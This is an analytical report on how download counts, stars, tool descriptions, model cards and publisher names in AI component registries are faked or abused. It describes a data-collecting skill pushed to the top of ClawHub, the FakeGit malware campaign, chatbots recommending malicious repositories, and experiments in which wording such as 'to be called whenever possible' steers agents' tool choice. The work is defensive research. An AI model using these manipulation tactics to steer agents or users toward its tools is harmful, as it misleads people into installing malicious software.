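Two security researchers found separate ways to inflate download counts on ClawHub, the marketplace for skills used by the AI assistant OpenClaw. One of them, Jamieson O'Reilly, founder of the security company Dvuln, published a harmless skill there early in 2026 and raised its count to more than 4,000. Developers in seven countries then downloaded it, according to The Stack, a technology news site. O'Reilly said the counter did not limit requests or check for repeat downloads by the same person.

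By March ClawHub protected its download counter by limiting the number of requests and counting each user or network address at most once an hour for the same skill. However, Silverfort's *Hijacking trust* describes a programming mistake that left open a second route to the counter, which bypassed every check. Silverfort, which sells identity security products, used this route to put a skill of its own at the top of its category. The skill posed as an email and calendar assistant, and sent Silverfort the username and network domain of whoever ran it. It ran about 3,900 times in six days, in more than 50 cities. These runs are better evidence of real use than a download count, though one user may account for many of them. Silverfort reported the flaw on 16 March, and ClawHub's developers fixed it within 24 hours.

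The counter's rules now apply to everyone, but limiting the count by IP address doesn't make it a reliable count of people, because an office of 200 may share one address and a single attacker may control hundreds.

### Why counting people is hard

Counting each person only once would prevent most fake stars, likes and downloads, but a website can count only accounts and addresses. Creating many false identities to gain influence in a system is called a Sybil attack. In *The Sybil Attack*, Douceur (2002) asks whether a group of computers can prevent such an attack without a central authority to verify identities.

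Without an authority to verify identities, the only direct way to prove that two accounts belong to different people is to set a task that one person could not do alone. Suppose each account must solve a puzzle that takes an ordinary laptop a minute. An attacker with 500 times a laptop's computing power can then pass as 500 people. If the accounts don't have to solve their puzzles at the same time, a single laptop can pass as any number of people by solving them one after another.

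Asking existing members to vouch for new ones doesn't help much. If a newcomer needs q members to vouch for it, an attacker who gets q false accounts accepted can use them to vouch for an unlimited number of others. Douceur concludes that the defence works only if all participants have nearly equal resources, all identities are checked simultaneously by everyone, and the number of members who must vouch exceeds the number of dishonest participants. None of these conditions is realistic for a large public system.

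GitHub, Hugging Face and ClawHub have central operators, so Douceur's argument does not rule out a reliable count on any of them. An operator could require a passport from everyone who gives a star. Swierzy and colleagues think tying counts to physical identities would make faking much more expensive without ending it. It would also deter many honest users, and people with genuine passports could still trade stars or give them in return for gifts.

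### Why cleverer formulas don't solve it

Cheng and Friedman proved in 2005 that a large class of formulas for calculating popularity cannot prevent faking when accounts are unverified. A site might try such a formula instead of verifying accounts, for instance by giving more weight to accounts that other people trust. The proof covers what Stannat, Ileri and colleagues (2021), in *Achieving Sybil-Proofness in Distributed Work Systems*, call global reputation, where everyone sees the same score, as with a star count.

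The theorem concerns formulas that rank participants in a network by the trust they express in one another. A formula is symmetric if it ignores names, so that relabelling the participants doesn't change anyone's score. An attacker can create extra identities and divide among them the trust the attacker already receives from others. For any symmetric formula, except a useless one such as giving everybody the same score, there are cases in which this raises the attacker's ranking, even with only one extra identity (Loiseau, 2016, *Network Economics*, a set of university lectures).

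Suppose 1,000 honest accounts have starred tool server A, and an attacker creates 1,000 accounts that star server B. The two halves of the network are identical except for the names, so a symmetric formula, which ignores names, has to give A and B the same score. Giving more weight to accounts with many followers doesn't help, because the attacker can create the followers too. PageRank, the method behind Google's original ranking of web pages, is symmetric and has this weakness.

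The theorem doesn't apply to formulas that treat some participants differently from the start. One such formula treats trust as water flowing through pipes from the person asking. Fake accounts can add pipes of any size among themselves, but all the water must still reach them through pipes from outside the group, so no fake account can score higher than the attacker could have scored without it. The attacker may still overtake someone in the ranking, although Loiseau lists another formula, PathRank, that prevents this too. Stannat and colleagues object that an attacker can still benefit from many fake accounts with modest scores. In a registry, for example, an attacker might list fifty copies of a malicious tool server, none of them ranked at the top.

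### What might work better than a raw count

He and colleagues suggest that GitHub give more weight to stars from accounts with a record of real activity, or quietly ignore stars from suspicious accounts. An account's age is useful because nobody can create a five-year-old account today. However, people can buy old accounts, and the lockstep accounts in He and colleagues' data had been active for about as long as ordinary ones. Activity records can also be faked, since Swierzy and colleagues note that GitHub displays whatever dates a project's owner gives for past changes to the code. Weighting stars by account history also disadvantages honest newcomers. *Manipulation-resistant reputation for peer-to-peer scientific publishing* (2026) cites earlier work by Friedman and Resnick showing that where new identities are easy to create, everyone has to distrust newcomers.

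Use by known organisations is probably more informative than stars, likes or download counts. Swierzy and colleagues recommend checking whether projects already confirmed to be genuine refer to the component. An attacker can create 10,000 packages that depend on a malicious one, but getting a well-run project to depend on it is much harder.

*Anduin* (Ramji, Zeng and colleagues, 2026) applies the same idea to services that AI agents pay for automatically, using records of 66 million payments with a median of one cent. Ranking services by number of customers is easy to manipulate, because an attacker can pay their own service from many accounts and lose only the transaction fees. Anduin instead starts from the services a buyer already pays, finds their other customers, and looks at what else those customers buy. An attacker can influence the result only if their accounts spend money at services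 the buyer already uses.

In simulated attacks on 813 buyers, manipulating the best-performing version cost 20% of what the buyers had spent, compared with 0.9% for a standard recommendation method. At that rate, an attacker would still need only about $8 to mislead a buyer who has spent $40. This version also ranked the new service a buyer chose next in first place in 23.6% of cases, against 3.7% for a simple ranking by use. The protection holds only if the attacker controls no service the buyer already pays, and a buyer with no history gets no recommendations.

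In the United States, a 2024 Federal Trade Commission rule prohibits buying or selling fake indicators of social media influence for commercial purposes, if the buyer knew or should have known that they were fake. It is unclear whether a star on a code-sharing site counts. If it does, the rule might discourage a start-up from buying stars to impress investors, because regulators can identify the company. The rule is unlikely to deter someone who publishes password-stealing software under a false identity, since that person is already committing a more serious offence.

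## Whether faked popularity changes what people and agents install

Fake stars and downloads do harm only if they lead someone to install a component they otherwise wouldn't. A higher number might persuade people who are already looking at the component, or it might raise the component's ranking so that more people see it. The two best experiments on human developers test persuasion but barely test the effect of ranking.

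### Two field experiments on Python packages

The 25 packages for which Shen and colleagues bought stars were part of a larger randomised experiment. They found 622 packages that had appeared on PyPI in the last week of April 2023 and had a public GitHub repository, and chose 100 at random to receive extra stars. They picked new packages because a star count should matter most when there is no track record. Twenty people, the researchers and their contacts, starred all 100. By 21 May the median gain was 20 stars for packages starred only by these people and 69 for those with bought stars as well. The median for the untreated packages was still zero.

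The added stars made no statistically significant difference to downloads after a month or at any of four later dates up to October. At one month, the median untreated package had 44 apparently human downloads, compared with 48 for packages with stars from contacts and 49 for those with bought stars. The extra stars also brought no detectable increase in code changes, bug reports or releases, and did not attract further stars from strangers.

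The result for bought stars is imprecise because it is based on 25 packages. The 95% confidence interval for the difference of five downloads runs from −42 to 52, so the stars could have doubled the median package's downloads without the experiment detecting it. Averages are even less informative, since a few packages dominate them. One package with bought stars, firebase-functions, passed 500,000 downloads, but it is an official product that Google had announced two days before the experiment began.

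In a second, much larger experiment, Shen and colleagues took a random sample of PyPI packages and kept 23,965 with at least five apparently human downloads. In early June 2023, a script downloaded 4,823 of them 100 times each. If a high count attracts users, the gap between these packages and the rest should have kept growing after the script stopped. A month later the gap between the medians was 75 downloads, and it stayed between 72 and 75 for the rest of the four months. The confidence interval for the gap's growth runs from −0.1 to 0.1 downloads a day, which allows at most about 15 extra downloads over 145 days.

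This result is precise, but it may be weak evidence about whether inflated download counts persuade developers. PyPI's project pages do not display download counts, so developers have to look them up elsewhere. If few people saw the inflated numbers, downloads would have stayed flat even if the numbers were persuasive.

Shen and colleagues kept the amount of faked popularity small for ethical reasons, and they don't rule out an effect from the larger, sustained campaigns that companies or criminals might pay for. Their data cover only Python packages in 2023. They also point out that a single organisation installing a malicious package could be seriously harmful, and that it is nearly impossible to design an experiment to detect such a rare event.

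They explain the null results by arguing that developers, who have to live with a bad choice, look beyond the star count to the documentation and the project's activity. This fits an earlier experiment they cite, in which fake upvotes on a news site led to more positive ratings, except on posts about information technology. An agent's user may check much less than a developer does.

The experiments also kept the packages too obscure to reach GitHub's trending page. The skill that Silverfort pushed to the top of its ClawHub category ran thousands of times in six days. This suggests that ranking matters, but nobody knows how often the skill would have run at a lower rank.

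### Whether fake stars attract real ones

He and colleagues looked for a promotional effect in existing data. They used a panel autoregression, a statistical model that predicts each repository's new stars in a month from its history. One version compares each repository with itself at other times, and also allows for months that were unusual for all repositories. Its estimates are:

log R(t) = 0.364 log R(t−1) + 0.148 log R(t−2) + 0.097 log R_total(t−3)
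 + 0.074 log F(t−1) + 0.029 log F(t−2) − 0.045 log F_total(t−3)
 + repository and month effects

R(t) is the number of real stars (those StarScout did not flag) gained in month t, and F(t) is the number of suspected fakes. The totals include all stars up to the month shown.

The model uses logarithms, so doubling one month's fake stars multiplies the next month's predicted real stars by 2^0.074, an increase of about 5%. The predicted increase in the month after is 2%. Doubling one month's real stars instead predicts 29% more real stars in the next month. Doubling fake stars more than two months old predicts about 3% fewer new real stars each month. He and colleagues conclude that fake stars promote a repository for less than two months and then become a liability.

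The evidence that bought stars cause a later decline in real ones is weak. He and colleagues acknowledge that an inexperienced maintainer might both buy stars and run a project that attracts little interest, in which case the purchase need not have caused the decline. Most of the star histories were also too short for a standard test of whether changes in fake stars help to predict later changes in real ones. The early gain could be partly an error too, because any bought stars that StarScout missed count as real. A seller who delivers stars over several weeks could therefore appear to have generated genuine interest.

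At first sight this early gain conflicts with the field experiment, in which extra stars attracted no others. But the predicted effect is too small for that experiment to have detected. Suppose the model uses the logarithm of one plus each count, a common way to handle zeros. Going from 0 to 69 fake stars would then multiply one plus the next month's real stars by:

70^0.074 ≈ 1.37

A new package that would otherwise have gained no stars would gain about 0.4 stars. He et al. also measured stars rather than downloads, so even a strong effect would not show that more people installed the packages.

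Someone spreading malware may not care about a liability that appears in the third month. The fake OpenAI model on Hugging Face topped the trending list in less than a day. The monthly model is more relevant to start-ups that buy stars and hope to keep their users.

### Malicious tool servers that agents recommended

When an agent chooses what to install, an attacker may not need fake popularity. Island's *AgentBaiting* (2026) describes FakeGit, a campaign of about 7,600 malicious GitHub repositories created by about 6,600 accounts. More than 800 posed as skills or MCP servers for services such as Gmail, WhatsApp and Databricks. Many copied real projects, and some came from accounts whose names closely resembled a real developer's. The repositories included instructions to download and run a file that installed a program for stealing passwords and active login sessions.

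The fake skills and servers appeared more than 600 times in public catalogues, including LobeHub, Glama, MCP.so and MCP Market. Island could not tell which listings the attackers had submitted and which the catalogues had copied automatically. Some catalogue pages reproduced the attackers' instructions, including the link to the malware. Island counted 14 million downloads of files from about 200 of the campaign's repositories, but that doesn't measure how many people ran the malware.

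Island then asked three AI products for components without giving them any links. It asked Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, for a free skill for writing "cinematic" prompts, with installation instructions. Claude Code searched the web and opened two repositories, one harmless and one from the campaign. It recommended the harmless one but offered the other as an alternative and repeated the malicious repository's instructions, including the advice to click past a Windows security warning. In other runs, Claude inspected the malicious repository more closely, recognised its contents as suspicious and refused to recommend it.

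Gemini and ChatGPT did worse. When asked for a link to a free Walmart MCP server, Gemini recommended a malicious repository first. ChatGPT listed the same repository among three options and called it the best place to start.

That repository had only five stars, so its popularity is very unlikely to have persuaded either model. Checking stars might even have helped identify some of the other fakes. For example, the campaign's copy of a well-known collection of skills had 63 stars, while the original had more than 67,000.

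These tests are anecdotes from a company that sells a secure browser to businesses. Island doesn't say how many times it ran each request or how many requests produced no malicious result. The requests were narrow, and there may have been few genuine free Walmart servers to recommend. The agents passed links or instructions to the user, and Island doesn't report that any agent installed the malware. Still, Claude's refusals show that an agent can sometimes spot the problem if it looks at the files.

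### Popularity claims in tool descriptions

Controlled experiments can isolate the effect of popularity from everything else in a listing. Faghih, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Gaming Tool Preferences in Agentic LLMs*, gave models a request and two copies of the tool needed to answer it. The copies were identical except for an extra sentence in one description. Each pair appeared in both orders, for a total of 516 test cases. The table shows the ratio of correct uses of the edited tool to correct uses of the original.

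| Claim added to the description | GPT-4.1 | Qwen2.5-7B |
|---|---|---|
| Over 1,000 GitHub stars | 1.18 | 0.99 |
| Over 100,000 GitHub stars | 1.16 | 0.99 |
| Trusted by over 100,000 users | 1.29 | 1.01 |
| Developed by Google | 1.43 | 0.99 |
| Actively maintained | 4.28 | 1.76 |
| Most effective tool, to be called whenever possible | 7.48 | 7.84 |

Claimed stars had a small effect on GPT-4.1 and none on Qwen, and claiming a hundred times as many stars made no difference. Asserting that the tool was the best and should be used had a far larger effect. Other models respond differently. In a larger set of tests, o4-mini, an OpenAI reasoning model, correctly used the version of the tool with a claim of 100,000 users in 58.8% of cases and the original in 27.3%.

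Newer models also respond to vague claims of popularity. In *Advertising to Agents*, Wang (2026) fixed the hypotheses and analysis in advance and tested two small OpenAI models, GPT-5.4-nano and GPT-5.4-mini. Each model chose between two tools whose listings differed only in the factor being tested. Describing a tool as popular among developers raised the rate at which it was chosen by 18 percentage points for nano and 16 for mini. A superlative such as "world-class" raised the rate by 31 points for nano and 39 for mini. Combining popularity, superlatives, endorsements and promises of good results raised it by 44 and 43 points, respectively.

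Wang then repeated the test on kinds of task held back from the main analysis. The combined praise still added 35 points for nano and 31 for mini, but no single kind of praise had a statistically clear effect. The test was too small to detect single effects below about 16 to 26 points, so it neither confirms nor refutes the effect of popularity wording alone.

A checkable specification, such as the resolution of a weather forecast, helped a tool about as much as a superlative did. Publishers therefore have much less incentive to make checkable claims, since writing "world-class" brings about the same benefit and can't be proved false.

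In most of these trials both tools could do the job, so the added words could only affect the choice between two adequate tools. Wang also tested praise for tools that could not do the job. Neither model chose a tool that covered the wrong region or language, however much it was praised. But when a tool's numerical limit was too low for the task, such as a 5 MB limit for a 300 MB file, nano chose it in 16% of trials without praise and 51% with combined praise.

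A study of shopping agents measures the strength of such claims in money. Buecheler, Berbeglia and Guo (2026), in *A Cue's Hidden Price*, showed models two matched products and added a sentence to one, for example that 10,000 customers had chosen it. They then raised that product's price until the model chose it only half the time. If S(g) is the share of choices it wins when it costs a fraction g more than its rival, the value of the sentence is the smallest g for which:

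S(g) ≤ 1/2

Across 113,472 trials, six of the added cues each led the model to choose the product carrying them at least 95% of the time when prices were equal, but the cues were worth from 1.6% to 21.4% of the price. A test with two identical tools can therefore make a weak claim look as powerful as a strong one. Buecheler and colleagues also tested Jev, a model that outputs a probability instead of text. Most of the sentences did not sway it, but the strongest claims of popularity did. Shopping choices are only a rough guide to software choices, because a model choosing a tool server has to judge whether the server can do a particular job.

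In all three studies, the popularity claim was text that a seller or publisher could write, so a false one costs nothing and requires no fake accounts. None of the studies varied the star or download count that a registry itself displays. Shen and colleagues recommend varying those counts in experiments with coding agents, which would also avoid deceiving human developers.

### What else affects an agent's choice

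The order in which tools are listed can affect an agent's choice more than anything the publisher writes. When Faghih and colleagues gave GPT-4.1 two tools with identical descriptions, it correctly used the first in 80.2% of cases and the second in 13.6%. In Wang's tests, the first of two identical listings led by 72 points, though in exploratory tests Claude Sonnet 4.6 chose the second more often. If a catalogue sorts by stars or downloads, faked counts could therefore affect an agent's choice even if the agent is never shown them.

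Even the labels on a tool's input fields affect the choice. Li, Qiao and Gao (2026), in *Which Metadata Matters for LLM Tool Selection in MCP?*, changed one part of a listing at a time for five models and five tasks. To separate the effect of the change from that of position, they used the model:

P(choose tool i) = exp(βx_i + γ_i) / Σ_j exp(βx_j + γ_j)

Here x_i is 1 if tool i has the more common or more complete version of the part under test and 0 otherwise, β is the effect of having that version, and γ_i is the effect of being in position i. For input fields, the median size of the statistically clear effects was 3.82, which multiplies the odds of being chosen by about 46 (e^3.82). For the server's name, it was 1.48, a factor of about 4.4.

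In one test, models chose an email tool only 1 to 10% of the time when its address field was called "recipient_id" instead of "to". Li and colleagues suggest that the models took the new label to mean an identification number. If so, the models were choosing based on whether the tool fitted the request, and another result supports this. When a request included sending a copy to a second person and only one tool had a field for that, all five models chose that tool, even when it was in second place. Choosing this way is sensible, but it doesn't protect against an attacker who copies a genuine tool's input fields.

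A close match between the request and the description was also the best predictor of choice in a study of seven models by Blankenstein, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *BiasBusters*. They gave each model 1,000 requests, each with five interchangeable services to choose from, and rotated the order. To measure favouritism they added up how far each service's share was from an equal share and halved the total:

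δ = ½ Σ |P_i − 1/5|

If one service gets 60% of requests and the other four get 10% each, δ is 0.4, meaning 40% of the choices would have to change to make the shares equal. The models scored between 0.25 and 0.37. Most of them favoured the same services, so a listing that attracts one model may attract several. The same seems to be true of skills, since every model tested in *Under the Hood of SKILL.md* (2026) chose copies with manipulated descriptions over the originals more than half the time.

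Genuine popularity may influence models through their training data. *A Study of LLMs' Preferences for Libraries and Programming Languages* (2025) found that all the models it tested heavily favoured well-established code libraries over fast-growing alternatives. *Do LLMs Favor Their Providers?* (2026) cites research in which models favoured particular cloud services, and sometimes replaced the service in a user's existing code without being asked. Buying stars today cannot change what a model has already learned, so this preference may protect users from new impostors when a famous library exists. It helps less when the user wants something obscure and the agent has to search. Blankenstein and colleagues strengthened a small model's preference for one service by training it further on text that mentioned the service repeatedly. An attacker who could plant enough text in future training data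 might do the same.

In Wang's exploratory tests, warning agents that some tools were commercial partners clearly reduced the choice of heavily advertised tools in only one of five models. Changing the tool listings worked better. When listings gave numerical limits in separate fields with no sales text, nano chose the capable tool in 88% of trials, compared with 49% when the limits were in prose beside praise for the weaker tool. However, someone would have to verify what publishers enter in those fields.

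Blankenstein and colleagues propose filtering out irrelevant tools and choosing at random among the rest. This treats honest publishers more fairly, but it gives a malicious server that passes the filter the same chance as any other. If one of five remaining servers is malicious, the agent would choose it 20% of the time, and the attacker could raise that to 50% by listing three more copies.

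## Model cards and component inventories

A component's description comes from its publisher, whereas stars and downloads are supposed to come from other people. A model's main description is its model card, which covers the model's purpose, training, test results and limits. Hugging Face displays the card on the front page of the model's repository. Software projects have a README, a text file that serves the same purpose, and each tool on a tool server has a short description.

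### What model cards were designed for

*Model Cards for Model Reporting* (Mitchell, Wu and colleagues, 2018) proposed the model card because people were discovering serious errors in models only after companies had deployed them. For example, commercial face recognition software could not pick out the face of Joy Buolamwini, a graduate student at MIT. Buolamwini and others later showed that such software made more errors on darker-skinned women.

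The proposed card is one or two pages long and has nine sections:

- model details, such as the developer, date, version and licence
- intended use, including uses the developer advises against
- factors that may affect performance, such as groups of people, cameras or lighting
- metrics
- evaluation data
- training data
- quantitative analyses, with results for each group and combination of groups
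- ethical considerations
- caveats and recommendations

The proposal centres on reporting results separately for each group. In a sample card for a smile detector, a much larger share of the "smiling" labels were wrong for older men than for any other group, which an overall accuracy figure would have hidden. The card format includes a version number but no hash, and none of its sections covers hidden behaviour or tampering.

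### How complete the cards are

In *What's documented in AI?*, Liang, Rajani and colleagues (2024) found that only 32,111 of the 74,970 model repositories on Hugging Face in October 2022 (about 43%) had a model card, although these repositories received 90.5% of all downloads. Of the cards, 74.3% had a section on training, but only 17.4% had one on limitations and 15.4% had one on evaluation. Among the 100 most downloaded models, 39% had a section on limitations and 47% had one on evaluation.

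Nearly all popular models now have a card. *Current Model Cards Are Insufficient for Downstream Governance of Open-Weight Foundation Models* (Chae, Kim and colleagues, 2026) found one for 498 of the 500 most downloaded models in January 2026. About three quarters had some safety-related content, which the paper measured by counting safety keywords. Downloads explained less than 1% of the variation in these counts. The publisher mattered more, with Meta and Google using many of the keywords and Qwen using few. Keyword counts are a crude measure because they can't distinguish a test result from a passing mention.

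Publishers still write more about how a model is built than about how it might fail. In a sample of 100 Hugging Face cards, *AI Transparency Atlas* (2025) found that over 90% covered architecture and evaluation metrics, but only about 20% covered interpretability (how people can understand the model's outputs). *Learning From the Best* (2026) found that 12 of 18 popular cards explicitly discussed intended use, limitations, risks or misuse.

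More detailed model cards seem to attract users. Liang and colleagues added detailed cards to 42 popular models that had little or no documentation, and compared their downloads over the three weeks before and after with those of 92 similar models. Downloads rose moderately. A Hugging Face employee wrote the cards, and the models didn't change, so better documentation is the most likely cause. Each card took about 40 minutes to write. A malicious publisher can do this as easily as an honest one, so under Spence's signaling theory a detailed card is weak evidence that its publisher is honest.

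### Which claims an outsider can test

A complete model card is useful as evidence only if someone can check its claims. Anyone who has the files can check the model's architecture and size and read its licence. Checking a benchmark score takes more work, because the tester needs the same test data, settings and scoring rules. Outsiders usually cannot test claims about training data or pre-release safety work, because the publisher keeps the records.

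Some safety statements are too vague to test. Chae and colleagues criticise warnings that a model "may generate harmful content", with no account of how anyone tested it or when it failed. They also found that publishers rarely disclose in a standard way whether they trained a model on another model's output, so users cannot tell where its behaviour came from.

OpenAI's (2026) model card for Privacy Filter contains claims of every kind. Privacy Filter is a small model that finds personal information in text, such as names and phone numbers, so that other software can remove it.

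| Claim in the card | What an outsider can do |
|---|---|
| Eight layers, 128 experts (subnetworks) in each, 33 output classes | Compare the configuration file and the weights |
| 1.5 billion parameters | Count the numbers in the weights file |
| Apache 2.0 licence | Read the terms, but not confirm that OpenAI holds every right it grants |
| F1 score of 0.926 for finding exact items | Repeat the test |
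| No training on the benchmark's training data | Look for signs of memorisation, without a conclusive answer |
| Training on public and synthetic data | Very little, since the card does not name the datasets |

A reader can roughly check the parameter count in a minute. The main weights file in OpenAI's Hugging Face repository is 2.8 GB. If each parameter takes two bytes, a common format, the file holds about 1.4 billion parameters, close to the figure in the card. An exact count requires reading the list of contents at the start of the file.

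The benchmark score is harder. It combines precision (P), the share of flagged items that really are personal information, with recall (R), the share of personal information that the model finds:

F1 = 2PR / (P + R)

OpenAI reports a precision of 0.940 and a recall of 0.980 on the PII-Masking-300k dataset, which gives an F1 of 0.960. These scores are based on tokens, which are words or pieces of words. F1 falls to 0.926 when the model gets credit only for marking an item's exact beginning and end.

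Uppala (2026), in *OpenAI Privacy Filter*, tested the public model on the same dataset and got 0.855 for exact items. The gap doesn't show that OpenAI's figure is wrong, because Uppala used 2,000 examples and OpenAI used about 47,700. Before testing, OpenAI also matched the dataset's labels to its own categories, dropped those with no equivalent and corrected some by rule. Such choices can move a score by several points, so a reader who knows only the score and the dataset's name cannot tell whether someone else has reproduced that score.

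OpenAI also reports a higher score, 0.942, after a further correction. A second model reviewed items that Privacy Filter had flagged but the dataset had not, and classified about 10,000 of them as real personal information that the dataset's makers had missed. Human reviewers checked 100 of these decisions and agreed with them all. The correction is reasonable, but it can only raise the score, because the review covered only these disputed items and not cases where the model and the dataset were wrong in the same way.

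Results on other languages differ far more. OpenAI reports an F1 of 0.895 on synthetic Russian text, while Uppala got 0.027 when testing for people's names in Ukrainian text from a general dataset. This may be partly because Privacy Filter is meant to mark private individuals, and news and encyclopaedic text mostly names public figures. But the model scored 0.397 on English text from the same collection, so it probably has trouble with Ukrainian. OpenAI warns in its model card that performance may drop on non-Latin scripts.

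The value of the benchmark also depends on OpenAI's statement, which outsiders cannot test, that it did not use the training portion of PII-Masking-300k. If OpenAI had trained the model on the dataset, a high score would be weaker evidence of how well it handles new text. In *Add data attribution section for AI transparency*, a public discussion of the card on Hugging Face, an outsider noted that the version on the site listed no training or evaluation datasets, and asked for at least a short disclosure of the training data. The proposal later narrowed to naming the evaluation dataset. Testers can partly avoid this problem by writing new examples that the model cannot have seen.

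### A true card on a malicious repository

The malicious repository that reached first place on Hugging Face in May 2026 had a nearly word-for-word copy of this card. According to HiddenLayer, the attackers kept the link to OpenAI's real PDF and changed the README in one place, to tell users to download the repository and run a program in it. In that program, the function that fetched the attackers' commands had a misleading name, which suggested that it verified the integrity of files.

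Nearly every technical statement in the copied card was true of OpenAI's model. A careful user could have repeated the benchmark on OpenAI's weights and confirmed the score, but still learned nothing about the program. The copy would have scored as high as the original for completeness, and higher than many honest publishers' cards. A good card is therefore no evidence against impersonation, and could even slightly favour an impostor.

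Copying takes almost no effort and is often legitimate. Another Hugging Face account openly duplicated Privacy Filter, including its README, weights and signature file.

A good model card doesn't show that a download is safe, and people who write cards can fairly say that cards were never meant as security evidence. Mitchell and colleagues wanted to help people use a model for suitable purposes, and they wrote that a card's accuracy "relies on the integrity of the creator(s)". They doubted that standards would prevent misleading cards in the near term, and recommended using cards alongside outside audits and adversarial testing. Privacy Filter's card serves the original purpose well, because it helps someone who already has the genuine model make a better decision about using it. It reports an F1 of only 0.545 on medical and legal questions before further training, and advises against relying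 on the model alone to anonymize text.

### READMEs and tool descriptions

A tool description has the same weakness as a model card, and an agent may also follow instructions the publisher puts in it, as in the WhatsApp demonstration. A README can have a similar effect. In Island's tests, Claude Code passed on a malicious repository's installation instructions.

Even honest descriptions are often wrong. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, compared descriptions with code for tools from 2,214 servers. They treat a tool as inconsistent if:

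claimed function ≠ actual function, or

some actual side effect is missing from the claimed side effects

A tool that merely warns of a side effect it doesn't have is not inconsistent by this definition.

Shi and colleagues used a language model to compare each tool's description with its code. When they asked whether the two matched, the model missed more than half of the real mismatches. When they asked it to look for mismatches, it raised too many false alarms. They therefore asked both ways and had the model settle any disagreement. This method flagged 1,907 (11.2%) of the 17,030 tools with usable descriptions and code, and it flagged at least one tool on 35% of the servers. Another 2,170 tools had no description.

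The most common problem, in 35.4% of the flagged cases, was a description that overstated what the code could do. About a quarter of the cases involved undeclared side effects. One tool was described as converting PDF files locally, but it uploaded them to an outside service. Another was described as asking for the user's approval before placing an order on a financial exchange, but it placed the order without asking. An agent relying on that description would reasonably expect a person to have the chance to refuse the order.

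The true rate of mismatches may be lower than 11.2%. On 400 real tools that people had also checked, the method correctly flagged 192 of 197 inconsistent ones and wrongly flagged 8 of 203 consistent ones. Consistent tools are much more common in the full collection, so false alarms make up a larger share of its results. If the error rates are the same there, the true share x satisfies:

0.975x + 0.039(1 − x) = 0.112

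This gives x ≈ 0.078, so about 8% of the tools would be inconsistent and roughly a third of the flagged ones would be false alarms. Even 8% is a serious problem for an agent that chooses tools by their descriptions and never sees the code.

### Bills of materials for AI

*Building an Open AIBOM Standard in the Wild* (2025) traces the bill of materials to manufacturing, where it is an inventory of a product's parts. Two of the main formats for software bills of materials are SPDX, developed under the Linux Foundation, and CycloneDX, which the security organisation OWASP first released in March 2018, according to *A Survey on Mapping Digital Systems with Bill of Materials* (2026).

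Both formats now cover AI. SPDX has an AI profile with fields for a model's type, training, limitations, test metrics, energy use and degree of autonomy, and a separate profile for datasets. CycloneDX has a component type for machine learning models that can include a model card. A shortened, illustrative CycloneDX entry for Privacy Filter might look like this:

```
{
  "type": "machine-learning-model",
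  "name": "privacy-filter",
  "version": "7ffa9a0",
  "purl": "pkg:huggingface/openai/privacy-filter@7ffa9a0",
  "licenses": [{ "license": { "id": "Apache-2.0" } }],
  "hashes": [{ "alg": "SHA-256",
               "content": "(hash of the weights file)" }],
  "modelCard": {
    "modelParameters": { "task": "token-classification" }
  }
}
```

The "purl" line is a standard address that tells software where to find this exact version.

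The main advantage of a bill of materials over a model card is that software can search it. If someone discovers that a model is unsafe to load, a company with thousands of applications can find every one whose bill lists that model. With good records of base models, the company could also find models trained from the unsafe one. But a search finds only what somebody recorded, and a publisher who hides a malicious part will not list it. A bill also contains little information about how the model behaves.

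Many bills come from tools that collect whatever a repository already contains. Erfan, Ryan and Rahman (2026), in *A Large-Scale Measurement of AI Bill of Materials Completeness*, ran OWASP's generator on 97,940 Hugging Face models, each with more than 100 downloads. The generator scores each bill out of 100. For each category of fields, it calculates:

category score = (fields present / total fields) × weight

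It then adds up the scores and reduces the total if important fields are missing. The average was 54.3, and no bill scored above 68.7. Every bill got the full 20 points for basic fields such as the format's name and version.

The AI-specific fields were filled in much less often. Datasets appeared in 39% of the bills, technical limitations in 17% and safety assessments in 10%. Almost all of the 97,940 bills had a description, but only 211 of the descriptions were more than placeholder text.

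The generator must have caused some of the gaps. None of the bills of materials included intended use or test metrics, although other studies find both in many model cards. The empty fields also include "autonomyType" and "useSensitivePersonalInformation", which are names from SPDX, but the generator writes a different format, CycloneDX. The low scores therefore show that automatically generated bills are poor, but not that publishers disclosed nothing.

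Erfan and colleagues measured whether fields were filled in, not whether they were correct, so the accuracy of these bills remains unknown. Because the generator relies on what the publisher wrote, it would copy any false claims.

Governments have asked for more disclosure, but mostly from the developers of the largest models. Chae and colleagues note that the European Union's AI Act and California's Transparency in Frontier Artificial Intelligence Act require developers to disclose safety risks, mainly for models trained with more than 10^25 and 10^26 operations respectively. Training typically takes about six operations per parameter for each token of text, so a model with 1.5 billion parameters would need more than 1,000 trillion tokens to reach even the European threshold. Most models that an agent might download are far too small to fall under these rules. The EU's Cyber Resilience Act,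 adopted in 2024, requires makers of digital products to draw up a software bill of materials covering at least the main dependencies. This duty was originally due to apply from December 2027, and it doesn't extend to the AI fields described above.

### Making the claims checkable

A claim in a card or bill is much easier to check if it includes the hash of the file it describes. A test result should also come with the test code and settings, and whoever ran the test should sign the result. For Privacy Filter, that would mean publishing the hash of the weights, the version of the dataset, the rules for matching and correcting labels, and the program that calculated 0.926. Uppala could then have run the same program to find out whether the lower score came from the sample, the scoring or the model. The signature would show who was responsible for the result, but it would not prove that the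 signer ran the test on those weights.

The hashes have to cover every file. The malicious Privacy Filter repository attacked its users through a program, so it could have done the same damage with OpenAI's genuine weights, and a hash of the weights alone would have matched. A full list of hashes would have revealed the extra program, but only if users got the list from OpenAI, because the attackers could have written their own list as easily as they copied the card. The tool announced in Sigstore's *Taming the Wild West of ML* addresses this by checking a model against both a signature and the claimed signer's identity.

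Claims about training data need records from the time of training. Hashes and test code don't help, because an outsider cannot reconstruct the data from the finished weights. Erfan and colleagues describe a system, AIBoMGen, that produces a signed bill of materials while a model is training, with hashes and details of the datasets and computing environment. This cannot help with the millions of models already on Hugging Face, because the record has to be made before the model is finished.

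## Publisher identity and digital signatures

The word "openai" at the top of a web page doesn't establish that OpenAI published what is on it. A name is a string of characters, while an identity is the person, organisation or automated process that controls the name. Linking the two takes evidence, and that link can later become invalid.

### How names mislead

The simplest trick is a lookalike name. *From unknown to verified*, by Stacklok, a company that makes software for running tool servers, gives the example of a server published under "@modelcontextportocol", with two letters of "protocol" swapped. The FakeGit campaign used lookalike developer profiles in the same way. An attacker can also use a company's exact name if the company has never registered it. *Practicalities of Malicious Models* (5stars217, 2024) reported that anyone could create a Hugging Face organisation under any unused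 name. Engineers who joined a fake organisation, thinking it was their employer's, gave its creator the power to change every model they uploaded there.

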